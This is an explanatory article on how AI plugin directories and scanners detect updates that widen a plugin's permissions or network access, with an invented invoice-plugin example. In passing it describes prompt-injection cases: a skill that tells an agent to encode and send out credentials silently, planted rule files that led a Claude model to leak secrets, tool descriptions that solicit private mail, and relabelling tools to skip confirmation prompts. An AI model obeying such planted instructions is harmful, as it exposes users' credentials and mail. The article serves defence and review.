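# Automatic scanning of AI plugins for broader permissions and new network access

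## What AI plugins can access and how scanners compare versions

An AI plugin is an add-on that gives an AI assistant or agent new instructions, tools or connections. An agent is a language model that can run commands, edit files and call other software. A plugin for an accounts department might contain instructions for handling an invoice, a script that reads PDF files and a connection to the company's email. People install plugins from online directories, which some companies call marketplaces, with a click or a one-line command.

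After a plugin is approved, its authors may publish new versions, some of which let it do, reach or read more than the approved version did. This is called scope expansion, and it can be part of ordinary product development or a means of theft. Directories, companies and makers of security tools therefore automatically scan new versions for wider permissions and new network destinations (the domains or addresses to which a plugin sends requests). Depending on the result, the new version is allowed through, blocked, or held for human review.

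Comparing versions is fairly easy for phone apps and browser extensions because the phone or browser enforces a fixed list of permissions, and an app cannot use one it never requested. Most AI plugins have no enforced list, so a scanner first has to work out what a plugin can access, which differs from one part of the plugin to the next.

### The parts of a plugin and whose privileges they use

Anthropic, which makes the Claude models, defines a plugin for its coding agent Claude Code as a directory of components that install and load as one unit: skills, hooks, MCP servers and a few others. OpenAI's *Plugin architecture* lists nearly the same components for ChatGPT and for Codex, OpenAI's coding agent. Anthropic says that a plugin runs with the user's own privileges: "what the plugin runs, it runs as you".

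A skill is a folder of written instructions, often with scripts, that an agent loads to perform a kind of task. Agent Skills' *Specification*, which defines an open format that works across several AI tools, requires only one file, SKILL.md, with a short block of metadata (the frontmatter) above ordinary prose. The prose has no privileges of its own, but it directs an agent that already has a shell, the user's files, a network connection and any keys the session can read, so adding a sentence can matter as much as adding a function. Scripts run as programs under the user's account. According to Anthropic, Claude Code also lets a skill file contain shell commands that run before the model reads the text, and the model sees only their output, not the commands themselves.

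Hooks are commands that run automatically at set events, such as the start of a session or just after the agent edits a file. The model does not control when they run. Anthropic's *Plugins reference* lists more than thirty events and several types of hook. One type runs a shell command. Another sends the details of the event to a web address, so a line in a settings file can add a network destination. Shell hooks have the user's full permissions, and Anthropic warns that they can modify or delete any file the user's account can access. OpenAI allows hooks only in plugins that people install by hand in the Codex desktop app.

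An MCP server is a program that offers tools to an AI application through the Model Context Protocol, an open standard. For each tool, the server publishes a tool definition containing a name, a description, an input schema that specifies the accepted arguments and their permitted values, and some labels about the tool's behaviour.

What a plugin's server can access depends largely on where it runs. A local server runs on the user's machine, and the Model Context Protocol's *Security Best Practices* says applications should warn people that it has the same privileges as the application that launched it. A remote server runs on its operator's machine and inherits no access to the user's computer. It receives the arguments the agent sends and any account access the user has granted. But outsiders can't read its code, and the operator can change what it does at any time. An August 2026 guide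 to plugin security from the software company Red Hat says that changing what a remote server returns takes no commit to the plugin's repository, so it triggers no review or automated test. OpenAI restricts the domains that a plugin's visual components can contact, but according to its *Security & Privacy*, the code on the server is limited only by the network restrictions of the machine that hosts it.

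Claude Code has a sandbox in which the operating system restricts access to files and network domains, but it covers only shell commands. Anthropic notes that the agent's file tools, MCP servers and hooks all run outside it. A script is therefore sandboxed when the agent starts it from the shell, but not when a hook starts it. An update that moves the script from the shell to a hook gives it broader access without changing its code.

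### Four meanings of "permission"

"Permission" can mean the access a plugin's author declares, the access a scanner infers from the plugin's files, the access a user or system grants, or the access the plugin uses. These four often differ, and a scanner can compare any of them across two versions.

A plugin's author declares its access in the manifest, the file that sets out the plugin's identity and components, or in a skill's frontmatter, but neither contains much detail. In Claude Code the manifest is optional and requires only a name. Its other fields cover metadata, components and user settings, which together do not give a list of the files or domains the plugin may reach. The Agent Skills format has an optional, experimental frontmatter field, `allowed-tools`, that lists pre-approved tools. In Claude Code, listing a tool there removes its confirmation prompt while the skill is active,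 but the agent can still call every other tool. A skill that lists only a file reader can still include instructions to run shell commands, and the user's ordinary permission settings then determine whether a prompt appears.

Pandey, Singh and colleagues (2026), in *Beyond Maliciousness*, measured how little skill authors declare. They scanned 6,309 skill listings from the middle of the popularity range on two marketplaces, skillsmp and ClawHub. (The scanner belongs to Metano Labs, where three of the paper's five authors work, and no third party has evaluated it.) Of the 6,061 listings with readable frontmatter, only 770 pre-approved any tools. Of those, 59% left out something the files could do, 39% listed something the files gave no sign of needing, and some did both. Only 166 lists matched their files. On phones and browsers, developers more often made the opposite mistake of asking for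 more than they used. Pandey and colleagues attribute the difference to enforcement, since leaving an item off a list that restricts nothing has no consequence for the author. Skill authors mostly left out shell commands and network access, the two items a reviewer of updates would most like to see.

Inferred access comes from a static scan, which inspects a plugin's files without running them. The scanner in this study, a language model combined with a few fixed rules, found evidence of shell commands in half of the listings, network access in 31% and access to credentials in 13%. These figures measure what the files make possible, not intent, and the scan can be wrong.

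Granted access is what the user, an administrator, the operating system or an outside service allows. For remote MCP servers, this usually means OAuth, the standard behind the screens that ask whether an app may use your account. Once the user agrees, an authorization server issues an access token with scopes, which are named permissions such as reading or sending mail. Under the authorization rules of the Model Context Protocol (2026), a server should list the scopes it requires when it requests authorization. If it lists none, the application requests every scope on the server's published list. When a later tool call needs more scopes, the server returns an "insufficient scope" error, and the application requests a new token that covers both the old and new scopes. Granted access can therefore expand in the middle of a task without a new version of the plugin.

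Published scope lists are an unreliable basis for a scanner's comparison. Under the Model Context Protocol, authorization is optional, and servers don't have to publish every scope they may request. Local servers are supposed to take their credentials from the machine's environment instead of using the protocol's authorization procedure, so that procedure gives the scanner no scopes to compare for them.

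Used access is what a plugin does when it runs, which runtime monitoring observes or controls. Pandey and colleagues ran nearly all of their listings in an isolated environment. Half could reach a shell according to the static scan, but only about one in twelve was seen using one. They recorded outbound requests for 286 listings, under 5%. Low counts are expected because a single session runs few of the paths through a plugin's code. In one family of listings, a setup script would have made lasting changes to the agent's configuration, but the test agent never ran it because no skill file mentioned it. The counts can also overstate what plugins do. In a smaller batch with a control run, the agent used the shell even without the skill, so some of the recorded activity belongs to the agent.

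### Comparing two versions

In outline, a version check runs like this:

1. Record the approved version, with a fingerprint of its files and a copy of its tool definitions.
2. Extract a list of its access: scopes, capabilities such as running shell commands, tool arguments, network destinations.
3. Extract the same list from the new version by the same method.
4. Subtract the old list from the new one.
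5. Pass the update, block it, or hold it for a person, under a rule fixed in advance.

The recording step is known as pinning. A fingerprint is a short code computed from a file's contents, and in practice any edit produces a different one. It covers only the files it was computed from, so if a plugin depends on an outside package with no fixed version, that package can change while the plugin's fingerprint stays the same. In the study of skills, 99% of the 2,871 listings that declared a dependency on outside software had at least one with no fixed version. A remote server has no files the scanner can fingerprint, so the scanner has to use the tool definitions instead.

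Extraction has to cover the whole plugin. Anthropic notes that plugins can add MCP servers, so a scanner that reads only the project's own server list can miss some. Network destinations are harder to extract because a program can assemble an address while it runs. The method also has to give stable results. When Pandey and colleagues scanned 89 listings again, the verdict was the same 84% of the time. Those verdicts were about threats, not permissions, but if a language model extracts the permissions, some of the reported differences between two versions may likewise come from the scanner.

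If A₁ is the set of access extracted from the approved version and A₂ is the set from the new one, the expansion is A₂ \ A₁, everything in A₂ that is not in A₁. This comparison can miss an expansion in two cases. First, the meaning of a permission can change while its name stays the same. The Model Context Protocol's security guidance lists changing what a scope allows without marking a new version as a common mistake. Comparing only names would also miss a change to an argument, such as a currency field that used to accept three codes and now accepts any text. Second, the approved version may already have broad access. If version 1 could run shell commands, version 2 can start uploading files without adding to its list of capabilities, because shell access already allowed uploads. Half of the skills in the study start with shell access, which is a good reason to compare specific destinations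 as well as broad capabilities.

Rules for the last step vary. A company might pass any update whose new domains are all on an allowlist, a list of permitted items with everything else blocked or flagged. The maker of the code editor Cursor doesn't need such a rule for its own directory because, according to Cursor's *Marketplace Security*, its staff manually review every plugin update. Even trivial updates therefore add to their work.

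### An invented update to an invoice plugin

Suppose that version 1 of an invoice plugin finds invoices in the user's inbox and records them in an accounting system. It holds a scope for reading mail, contacts one domain, and has a tool called `record_invoice` that accepts a supplier, a date and an amount. Version 2 arrives, and the comparison produces three lines:

```
+ destination   convert.invoice-tools.example
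+ scope         mail.send
+ argument      record_invoice.notes (any text)
```

| Addition | Legitimate explanation | Malicious explanation |
|---|---|---|
| New domain | The author moved PDF conversion to an outside service | Whoever runs the domain keeps a copy of every invoice |
| Scope for sending mail | Users wanted automatic reminders for late payers | The plugin can mail documents out, or send false payment requests from the user's own address |
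| Free-text argument | Accountants wanted to write "paid in two parts" | The tool's description tells the agent to paste in other mail, which then reaches the server as an ordinary argument |

An honest author and a thief both produce these three lines. Reading the code more closely may distinguish them in some cases, such as when a script uploads the whole mailbox but needs only one PDF. It may not help with the new domain, because the plugin sends a PDF to the conversion service either way. The plugin's files can be identical, since the theft happens on a computer that the scanner cannot inspect.

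The three additions look riskier together than separately because the plugin can now read private mail, take in text written by strangers and send data out. Pandey and colleagues found 628 skill listings with that combination and 397 with both credential access and network access, and they suggest that marketplaces manually review these groups first. This is a sensible way to prioritize reviews, but the combination is little evidence that a plugin is malicious, since a working mail assistant needs it too. The 628 listings had a possible route for leaking data, but no leak was observed.

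### How often a scanner is wrong

A scanner's recall is the share of malicious plugins it flags, and its false-positive rate is the share of harmless plugins it flags. For updates, the same definitions apply to versions. If a scanner holds for review every update that expands a plugin's access, its false-positive rate is the share of harmless updates that do so. Its recall falls with every malicious update that uses only the access the plugin already had.

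How much a flag should worry anyone depends on both rates and on how common malice is to begin with:

odds of malice after a flag = odds before × (recall ÷ false-positive rate)

If a scanner with 90% recall and a 5% false-positive rate checks 1,000 updates, 10 of them malicious, it flags 9 of the malicious updates and about 50 of the harmless ones, so roughly 15% of the flagged updates are malicious. If a given difference between versions appeared equally often in harmless and malicious updates, flagging it would not help distinguish them.

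Published figures often give neither rate. Pandey and colleagues read in full 140 listings drawn at random from the 5,971 that their scanner had judged benign, and found no missed threats. This implies, with 95% confidence, that at most about 2.1% of the 5,971 were threats, or about 125 listings. The scanner had flagged only 338 listings, so even if all of them were real threats, which the human review had not yet established, recall could be as low as 73%.

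## Anthropic's plugin directory: scanning every new commit

Anthropic runs a directory of plugins that people can add to the Claude chat app, Cowork (Anthropic's agent for office work) and Claude Code. Plugin authors keep their files and release updates on GitHub, a site for hosting code. Each saved set of changes is called a commit and is identified by a hash computed from its contents. Anthropic reviews plugins one commit at a time, so an approval covers a fixed set of files and any later edit needs a new scan.

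### Submitting the first version

To list version 1 of the invoice plugin, its author enters the repository's address in the developer portal, along with the branch or tag that Anthropic should follow for new versions. A branch moves forward whenever someone adds a commit, while a tag stays on one commit until someone moves it. If the plugin is one folder in a larger repository, Anthropic reads and scans only that folder.

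The author then runs a validation that checks the manifest, the README, the license and the rest of the folder. Some problems block the submission until the author fixes them. The result applies to one commit, so the author has to validate the plugin again after pushing any change, even a typo fix.

Anthropic then asks whether the plugin handles personal data, how long it keeps what it receives, whether it is meant for under-18s, and whether any data goes to a service that the author hasn't declared as a connector. (Connector is Anthropic's word for an MCP server that people connect to Claude.) The manifest has no field for the answer to the last question. If version 1 had already used an outside PDF converter that wasn't a declared connector, an honest author would have had to answer yes.

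But authors answer these questions in the portal, while updates arrive through GitHub. Anthropic tells authors they needn't return to the portal after the first submission unless a version is held or they want to change a setting. They can edit their answer on whether the plugin collects or transmits user data, but Anthropic describes no step in an ordinary update that requires them to. An author who adds a network destination in version 2 could easily leave the old answer in place.

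When the author submits the plugin, Anthropic takes the newest commit on the chosen branch or tag, repeats the validation and runs a security scan. There are three possible outcomes:

- **Passes every check.** The version is ready to publish.
- **Held for a reviewer.** An Anthropic reviewer reads the version and must clear it before it can go live.
- **Doesn't pass.** The portal lists the rules that the version breaks. If it failed the security scan, the portal also shows the category of the finding when the scan recorded one. Anthropic's example of a category is "Sends data to an undisclosed destination".

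### Whether wider access holds a version

That category shows that the security scan checks, to some extent, where a plugin's data goes. Judging by its name, it covers destinations that the author hasn't disclosed. A plugin's first version could therefore fail for sending data to an undisclosed destination, while its second could add a new destination without failing for it if the author disclosed it. Anthropic's submission page doesn't define disclosure, which might mean naming the destination in the portal answers, the README or a privacy policy.

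The same page doesn't list the findings that hold a version for a reviewer. Anthropic refers authors to a separate plugin pre-submission checklist for those findings, and to a page called "Prepare for the security scan" for what the scan looks for. Neither the submission page nor Anthropic's guide to updating a plugin makes clear whether a new domain or a broader permission is enough to hold a version. A company that relies on the directory therefore can't conclude from those two pages that a person has looked at every update that widens a plugin's access.

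Anthropic also doesn't describe comparing the new version with the old one. It says that an update gets the same validation and security scan as the first submission. This scan can catch a malicious addition, but it tests whether the new version breaks a rule, not whether it can do more than the last one. If the invoice plugin gains permission to send mail, the scan may treat that permission exactly as it would have in version 1.

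Anthropic's Software Directory Policy sets the rules for plugins. They may collect only the data from the user's context that they need to do their job, and they may not extract data from Claude's memory, the chat history or uploaded files. The policy also forbids hidden or encoded instructions, and it forbids directing Claude to fetch instructions about its behaviour from an external source. Otherwise, a skill could tell the agent to load the day's instructions from a web address, and its author could change what the agent does without making a commit.

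The policy also requires developers to verify that they own or control any domain their software connects to, except that a plugin may also connect to any connector approved in the directory. An honest author who hired another company to convert PDFs at the invoice plugin's new domain, `convert.invoice-tools.example`, would break this rule unless that company's service was an approved connector. A thief who registered the domain would satisfy the rule while breaking the ones on data collection, and checking who owns the domain wouldn't reveal that.

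### Who publishes an update

A version that passes doesn't go live until someone publishes it. Anthropic decides which publish setting applies to each plugin, and it describes three:

| Publish setting | First version | Later versions that pass |
|---|---|---|
| Default | The author requests publication and a reviewer publishes | The same, every time |
| Reviewer publishes only the first version | The author requests publication and a reviewer publishes | Go live by themselves |
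| Author publishes the first version | The author publishes, after a reviewer has approved the plugin and applied this setting | Go live by themselves |

Under the second and third settings, authors can turn automatic publishing off, and it also stops while the plugin is waiting for a reviewer.

The setting makes a large difference to an update that expands access. By default, a reviewer at Anthropic handles version 2 of the invoice plugin even if the scan finds nothing, though Anthropic doesn't say how closely the reviewer reads a passing version before publishing it. With automatic publishing, version 2 reaches the directory without a person seeing it unless the scan holds or fails it, so the list of findings that hold a version matters much more. In June 2026 Anthropic told users that submissions got a "basic automated review", that plugins with an "Anthropic Verified" badge had received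 additional review, and that there were limits to what it could review.

Automatic publishing also makes the security of the author's repository more important. The portal checks that the author can push to the repository before it lets them submit the plugin, publish it or turn on automatic publishing. An ordinary update requires none of those actions, only merging a change into the tracked branch. Anyone who takes over an account that can merge can therefore get a new version scanned and, if it passes, published to users. Red Hat advises plugin maintainers to block direct pushes to the main branch and require a second person to approve every merge, with no exception for administrators. This is sound advice, but users can't easily tell whether an author follows it.

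### After a failed scan

If a plugin has never been published and fails the security scan, Anthropic rejects the submission and stops scanning it until the author resubmits. If a plugin is already published, the directory keeps serving the last published version while a newer one is on hold or has failed, so users don't lose a working plugin because of a bad update.

After a plugin fails a security scan, Anthropic also blocks later versions until a reviewer clears the plugin, even if the author has removed the offending code. Without this rule, an attacker could keep adjusting a malicious update until one got through. But an honest author who trips the scanner by mistake must also wait for a reviewer before releasing anything, including a fix for a security hole. Authors can appeal each decision once, but a new commit replaces the refused version and ends the appeal, so an author who thinks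 the scanner was wrong has a reason to wait without changing the code.

Keeping the last version up protects users only if that version was safe. Anthropic's community marketplace is a catalog of third-party plugins for Claude Code, and a pull request (a proposed change to a repository) open there in April 2026 contained a harsher rule. Anthropic would rescan the source repositories every night and remove, without notice, any plugin that failed validation or safety scanning. This would take compromised plugins out of the catalog sooner, but it would also remove harmless plugins that the scanner wrongly flagged.

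### Pinning a plugin to a commit

Scanning a commit protects users only if they install that commit. In July 2026 Anthropic said that its community marketplace pinned each plugin to a specific commit by its hash. With pinning, a new commit in the author's repository has no effect on installations until Anthropic changes the hash in the catalog. If the catalog held only the repository's address, an attacker could submit clean files, wait for them to pass and then push malicious ones, and everyone who installed the plugin after that would get files that nobody had scanned.

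According to Red Hat's August 2026 guide, the marketplace for Claude Code plugins has no pinning by content hash, and a user who reinstalls a plugin gets whatever is on the default branch at that moment. This conflicts with Anthropic's documentation for its community marketplace. It may be true of some other marketplaces, since anyone can put a catalog in a git repository and invite people to add it.

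Pinning also depends on the agent that installs the plugin. A flaw found in 2026 let plugin code differ from its pinned commit in four coding agents. Help Net Security's *Zero-click RCE vulnerability hit four major AI coding agents, two remain unpatched* (2026) reported fixes in Claude Code 2.1.179 and Codex 0.146.0 but none for GitHub Copilot or Gemini CLI.

How soon a published update reaches a user depends on where the plugin came from. By default, automatic updates are on for Anthropic's main official marketplace and off for the community marketplace and third-party marketplaces. When they are on, Claude Code checks for updates after a session starts and replaces the copies on disk. The current session keeps the version it has already loaded, and the next session loads the new one. Plugins that users turn on in their claude.ai accounts instead sync to Claude Code in the background each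 time it starts.

Users learn less about an update than about a first installation. Before installing a plugin from the official marketplace, they can open a pane that lists the commands, skills, hooks and servers it will add. After an automatic update, they see only the plugin's name and a command to reload it. For a plugin synced from claude.ai, they see only that plugins have changed. Neither notice lists what the update changed, even if it added a hook that runs at the start of every session.

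### The separate scan for Enterprise organizations

Companies also use plugins that never go through the directory, such as a folder of skills from a consultant. For Enterprise customers, Anthropic offers a second scan, which checks third-party skills and plugins when someone in the organization uploads or edits them. It is on by default for organizations that had not chosen a setting before October 2, 2026. In other organizations, an owner can turn it on. Anthropic's *Get started with skill and plugin scanning* explains that Claude reviews the contents, usually within a minute or two, and returns one of three results. After a pass, the plugin installs normally. A warning means Claude couldn't fully verify the plugin, but users can still use it after acknowledging a caution banner. A fail means the scan detected malicious content and blocked the plugin.

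The scan uses a language model, which is important because much of a plugin is prose. Red Hat gives an invented example of a skill that checks a project's configuration file. In the tampered version, a few added sentences tell the agent to first read the user's cloud and GitHub credentials and put them, encoded, into a web address, supposedly to choose the right settings. They also say there is no need to mention this to the user. Red Hat points out that the usual tools analyse code, but its conclusion that skill files have no automated defence is too strong, since a language model can read those sentences as easily as a person can. Anthropic's description of the scan doesn't give its recall or false-positive rate, so it doesn't show how reliably Claude spots such sentences.

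An owner, or someone whose role lets them manage the organization's plugin libraries, can override a warning or a block by selecting "Allow anyway". Anthropic is introducing this option gradually, so some organizations may not have it yet. The override covers only one version of the plugin, and Anthropic scans the next version afresh. It applies to everyone with access to the plugin, so colleagues who might have hesitated after seeing the banner no longer see it.

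Anthropic lists several things that the scan doesn't cover:

- skills and plugins that were in the organization before the scan was turned on
- skills that people create with Claude
- skills shared through a connected MCP server
- MCP servers themselves
- organizations that manage their own encryption keys, have Anthropic retain no data, or use a configuration for HIPAA, the US law on health information

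Because of the first exclusion, a company that turns the scan on learns nothing about the plugins its staff already use. A later edit to one of those plugins should trigger a scan. The last exclusion leaves out hospitals and other organizations with some of the most sensitive data.

Anthropic also says that the scan looks for plugins built to misuse the access they are given, and that it won't catch a non-malicious skill that does something the user didn't intend. Suppose version 2 of the invoice plugin sends invoices to an outside converter and asks for permission to send mail, both for the reasons its author gives. If the scan works as Anthropic describes, this version should pass. A company that forbids sending invoices to outside services, or that wants to know whenever a plugin gains the ability to send mail, needs a different check.

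### Remote servers change without a commit

Suppose the tool `record_invoice` runs on the plugin author's remote server. The plugin's files contain the server's address but not its code. Anthropic scans the commit on Monday and it passes. On Tuesday the author adds a free-text argument, `notes`, and writes in its description that the agent should paste in any related mail. The repository has no new commit, so no scan runs, and the pinned hash still matches.

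An author who lists a plugin that uses their own remote server should also submit the server separately, as a connector. Anthropic automatically scans the connector for compliance with its policy and lists it as "Community" by default. Listings that Anthropic's system flags as highly useful may go on to a slower "Verified" review, in which reviewers test each tool.

After that, developers can add, change or remove tools by updating the server, without resubmitting it. A reviewer approves changes to the tool names on the directory page, but Anthropic treats those names as part of the listing. The server may already offer a tool that the listing doesn't mention. Some server updates also affect when Claude asks for confirmation. Claude can run tools labelled read-only without asking each time, but always asks before running those labelled destructive. The labels come from the server, so a developer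 who relabels a tool may remove a prompt that users had relied on.

In July 2026, Anthropic's *Manage your listing after publishing* stated that "there is no scheduled re-review" of MCP servers and that Claude picks up new tools the next time it connects. Anthropic has since removed the wording about re-review, which might reflect a change in practice or just a rewritten page. The Software Directory Policy mentions "initial and ongoing reviews" but gives no schedule or method, whereas OpenAI compares the tool definitions of live servers every day.

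A plugin's behaviour can also change through files on the user's machine. Hookify, a plugin in Anthropic's official marketplace, read rule files from whatever project the user had open and passed their contents to the model through a channel the model trusted. According to Red Hat, researchers at Pluto Security put five malicious rules, worded as ordinary project conventions, into such files. All five got Claude Opus 4.6 to leak local secrets, and the model didn't flag any as an attack. Anthropic closed the report, reasoning that a user who chooses to trust a project folder also trusts the instructions in it. Scanning Hookify's commits might have revealed the risky design but not the malicious rules, which were in other people's repositories.

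Anthropic leaves part of the monitoring of remote servers to users, advising them to connect only to developers they trust, review the scopes a connector requests, and watch for unexpected changes in how its tools behave. Anthropic's *GoPlus AgentGuard* (2026), the directory listing for a connector that scans other people's skills for malicious code, warns that Anthropic cannot verify that a connector's tools will work as intended or that they won't change.

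## OpenAI's plugin directory: daily comparison of tool definitions

OpenAI runs a single plugin directory for ChatGPT and Codex. Like Anthropic, it scans a plugin's files when the author submits them. It also checks the tool definitions that a remote MCP server publishes, which a scan of commits can't cover. OpenAI keeps a copy of the approved definitions, fetches the current ones every day and compares the two.

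### What OpenAI copies from the server

The author uploads the plugin as a ZIP file and connects its MCP server in OpenAI's developer portal, which then scans the server. OpenAI's *Remote MCP server review requirements* lists what the scan copies:

- each tool's name, title and description
- its input schema, and its output schema, which describes what the tool returns
- its security schemes, which state how the tool authenticates users
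- its behaviour labels and any extra metadata fields
- details of the plugin's visual interface, if it has one, including the domains the interface may load from or contact
- the server's instructions, which are general guidance for the model on using the tools together

The last item is fairly new. According to OpenAI's *Plugin UI changelog*, ChatGPT began reading server instructions in May 2026.

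Once the plugin is published, users get the tool definitions from OpenAI's copy, while each tool call goes to the live server. A developer therefore gains nothing by having the server send harmless definitions to the scanner and different ones to everyone else.

OpenAI used to freeze its copy of a plugin's published tool definitions. In the developer forum thread *How to surface mcp server updates for an existing plugin*, jbrodriguez asked why a small edit to a tool's description hadn't reached ChatGPT. jbrodriguez was told that this was expected, and that any change to a tool's name, description or schema needed a new version, a new scan and another review. An older rule, which a developer quoted in *Widget uri versioning and app resubmission*, described published definitions as "locked for safety". By November 2026 OpenAI had replaced the freeze with what it calls continuous review. Developers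 can now ship tool changes faster, but most of those changes no longer go through a formal review.

### New, changed and deleted tools

OpenAI's *Upload and submit your plugin* says that OpenAI scans each published server daily. A developer who has just deployed a change can also request a scan immediately. How a change reaches users depends on what changed:

| Change | What must happen before it reaches users |
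|---|---|
| The server drops a tool | Nothing more than a scan, which removes the tool |
| The server adds a tool | The tool passes automated checks |
| A tool's description, schema, security scheme or labels change | The new definition passes automated checks; until then, users keep the old one |
| The server's shared instructions change | The checks finish without holding an update to an existing tool or finding a problem in the instructions |
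| A skill or the listing text changes | The author uploads a new ZIP, gets it through review and publishes it |
| The server's code or the data it returns changes | Nothing; the change takes effect when the operator deploys it |

In OpenAI's example, the developer of a notes server adds a tool called `create_note`, lets `search` accept a folder, and deletes `archive_note`. The next scan removes `archive_note`. If `create_note` passes but the checks hold the change to `search`, users get the new tool and keep the old `search`. The portal shows the developer the held and live definitions, along with the issues found.

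Deleting a tool only reduces what a plugin can do, so it needs no check. If a check on a new or changed tool doesn't finish, OpenAI doesn't approve the update, even if the check had found no problems by then.

Comparing definitions shows OpenAI which tools have changed, but OpenAI may not hold every change that adds access. Its documentation doesn't list the findings that hold an update, and its *Plugin guidelines* don't forbid a tool from gaining access. They require input fields to relate directly to the tool's purpose, and they forbid "just in case" fields and requests for the whole conversation. Suppose the operator of the invoice server adds a free-text argument, `notes`, to `record_invoice`. If the argument's description tells the agent to paste in related mail, OpenAI has good grounds to hold the update. If the description asks for anything the accountant should know, the update would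 probably pass, although the agent might put the same mail in the field. Holding every such addition would be safer, but the amount of extra work depends on how often ordinary updates widen a schema.

OpenAI evaluates each tool change independently, so one bad description needn't block an unrelated fix. But a tool's risk often depends on the tools available alongside it. The maintainers of the Model Context Protocol (2026) say that a tool that searches email is neither safe nor dangerous on its own. If one update lets the invoice plugin read mail and another lets it send mail, each tool may look ordinary when checked alone.

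The comparison also works only if definitions are specific. A tool called `run_operation` that accepts the name of any operation could gain new abilities while its definition stayed the same. OpenAI therefore requires a separate tool for each operation the model can call and forbids using a generic tool to reach operations that reviewers haven't seen.

### Labels that the developer supplies

Each definition includes three labels that describe the tool's behaviour. The protocol calls them annotations, and OpenAI requires developers to set each one to true or false:

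- **`readOnlyHint`** is true if the tool only retrieves, computes or previews something. It is false if the tool changes anything outside itself, starts a job, sends a message or uploads a file.
- **`destructiveHint`** is true if a tool that makes changes might delete, overwrite or cancel something, revoke access, or do something irreversible. It is false for read-only tools and for tools that only add things.
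- **`openWorldHint`** is true if the tool deals with public or open-ended entities, as a web search does, or can send to arbitrary destinations. It can be false for a tool confined to one private account or workspace, even if another company hosts it.

A scanner that looks for new network destinations can't rely on the third label, because OpenAI says that connectivity alone doesn't determine its value. A tool that sends every PDF to one fixed conversion company might still count as closed. The definition has also shifted. In August 2026, OpenAI's *Define tools* set the label to true for tools that can affect public or external systems, which seems to exclude the read-only web searches that the guidelines include.

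`destructiveHint` has unclear cases too. OpenAI tells developers in its server requirements to set it to true for irreversible outcomes and false otherwise, but its guidelines say that being able to undo an action isn't enough to justify false. A developer could therefore choose either value for a tool like `archive_note` if it hides a note that the user can restore.

These labels can determine whether a user is asked before a tool runs. *When Neither Side Confirms* (Yao, Yang and colleagues, 2026) traced the source code of 41 open-source applications and developer kits that connect to MCP servers. In 39 of them, labelling a tool destructive made no difference to whether the user got a prompt. The command-line version of Codex was an exception. It skips the prompt if the server labels a tool read-only and non-destructive, or non-destructive and closed-world. Relabelling a tool could therefore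 remove a prompt in Codex, as it can in Claude. Continuous review makes this harder for plugins in the directory, because a changed label has to pass the checks like any other definition change.

The developer writes both a tool's label, such as "read-only", and the description that a checker would compare it with. An automated check can easily catch a tool called `delete_note` that is labeled read-only. The mismatch is harder to catch if the tool is called `tidy_notes` and its description doesn't mention deleting. The maintainers of the Model Context Protocol warn that a server can claim to be read-only and delete files anyway, so under the protocol, applications should not trust labels from untrusted servers. *Description-Code Inconsistency in Real-world MCP Servers* (2026) recommends that descriptions disclose external data flows and that applications check tools for consistency before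 offering them. OpenAI doesn't have the code of a remote server, so it can't check the description against it.

OpenAI's documentation is inconsistent about whether developers must also justify their labels. In July 2026 OpenAI required a written justification for every value on every tool. By October its guidelines no longer required justifications and let a developer explain a label on appeal if the automated review flagged it. In November the server requirements still described how to write justifications. Under those requirements, a justification can't override a label, so calling a tool "functionally read-only" has no effect if the server labels it otherwise. Dropping the requirement probably weakens security only slightly, since a dishonest developer would have written the justification too.

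OpenAI's requirement for explicit values is stricter than the protocol, which makes labels optional and tells applications to assume the worst if they are missing. The requirement ensures that the fields are filled in, but not that developers think about them. *What a Random Draw from the MCP Registry Contains* (2026) found no labels on 1,626 of 2,766 tools (58.8%). Of the 194 servers with tools, 72 labelled every tool and 122 labelled none, so many labels may come from a template or a house rule rather than a decision about each tool. *When Tool Calls Succeed but Workflows Fail* (2026) found one combination of labels on 39.9% of the tools it measured, in a collection dominated by a single publisher, and concluded that a label's presence is weak evidence that anyone chose it.

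Some labels are also wrong. Yao and colleagues estimated that about 5% of the destructive tools flagged by their extraction program had no confirmation step on the server and were labelled read-only or non-destructive. Their sample came from the official MCP registry, where nobody had applied OpenAI's checks. Two language models with access to the code agreed in 89% of cases on whether a tool was destructive, so some of the labels that OpenAI flags will be matters of opinion. In *Clarification needed on rejection feedback*, a developer quoted a rejection for labels that did not appear to match the tools' behaviour, and asked whether the rule also covered a fourth label that the documentation listed as optional.

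### Which network traffic the rules cover

Before connecting a server, the developer must prove control of its domain by placing a token from OpenAI at a set address on that domain or an eligible parent domain. This stops people from submitting someone else's server as their own, but it doesn't show what happens to data sent to the server.

The strictest network rule applies to the plugin's visual interface, such as a form or a table of invoices shown in the conversation. The interface runs in an isolated frame under a content security policy, which lists the domains it may use. The Model Context Protocol has separate lists for domains the interface may contact, load files from, or embed as pages, and OpenAI requires developers to list exact domains. The browser blocks any domain that isn't listed, so developers have a reason to declare every one the interface needs.

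Adding a domain to the policy counts as a change to the tool's definition, so it must first go through the automated checks. OpenAI's *App Security Whitepaper* (2026) says that the interface can contact only the plugin's declared server endpoints by default, and that OpenAI must approve any broader access, which it logs and can revoke. The interface's content can change without a scan if its address stays the same and it remains compatible. New code in the interface still can't contact an unlisted domain directly, but it can send data to the plugin's own server, which can forward the data.

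Embedded pages weaken this control because they follow their own policies. An interface can show a web page in a frame if the plugin's policy names the page's origin. OpenAI lets plugins embed pages from the domain that their server belongs to, so a server at api.example.com can embed app.example.com. It allows pages from other companies' domains only when they are essential. The developer must explain what each page does, why the plugin embeds it and who controls the domain. In July 2026 OpenAI blocked a submission if the scan found an external frame domain that the developer hadn't explained. A person has good reason to read these explanations, because the plugin's list doesn't limit where an embedded page sends data.

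OpenAI also fixes the server's origin, meaning its scheme (such as https), hostname and port. According to OpenAI's server requirements, a developer who wants a different origin must submit a new plugin and repeat the whole review, while a change to the path after the hostname needs only a new version. *Upload and submit your plugin* instead tells developers to contact support if they want to change the URL. Under either procedure, a routine update can't send users' tool calls to a different host. But whoever controls the hostname can point it at another machine without changing the origin.

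Some trusted developers can submit an address pattern, such as `https://{workspace}.example.com/mcp`, so that each customer connects to a separate endpoint. They also give OpenAI one working example for review and automated checks. Customers' endpoints could run different code from the example.

None of these rules covers what the server sends to other services, since OpenAI places no network restrictions on the server's code. If the operator of the invoice server starts passing PDFs to `convert.invoice-tools.example`, the origin, the interface's policy and the tool definitions all stay the same. OpenAI requires a privacy policy that names the categories of recipients, so an honest operator might have to update it, but may not need to if it already mentions "service providers".

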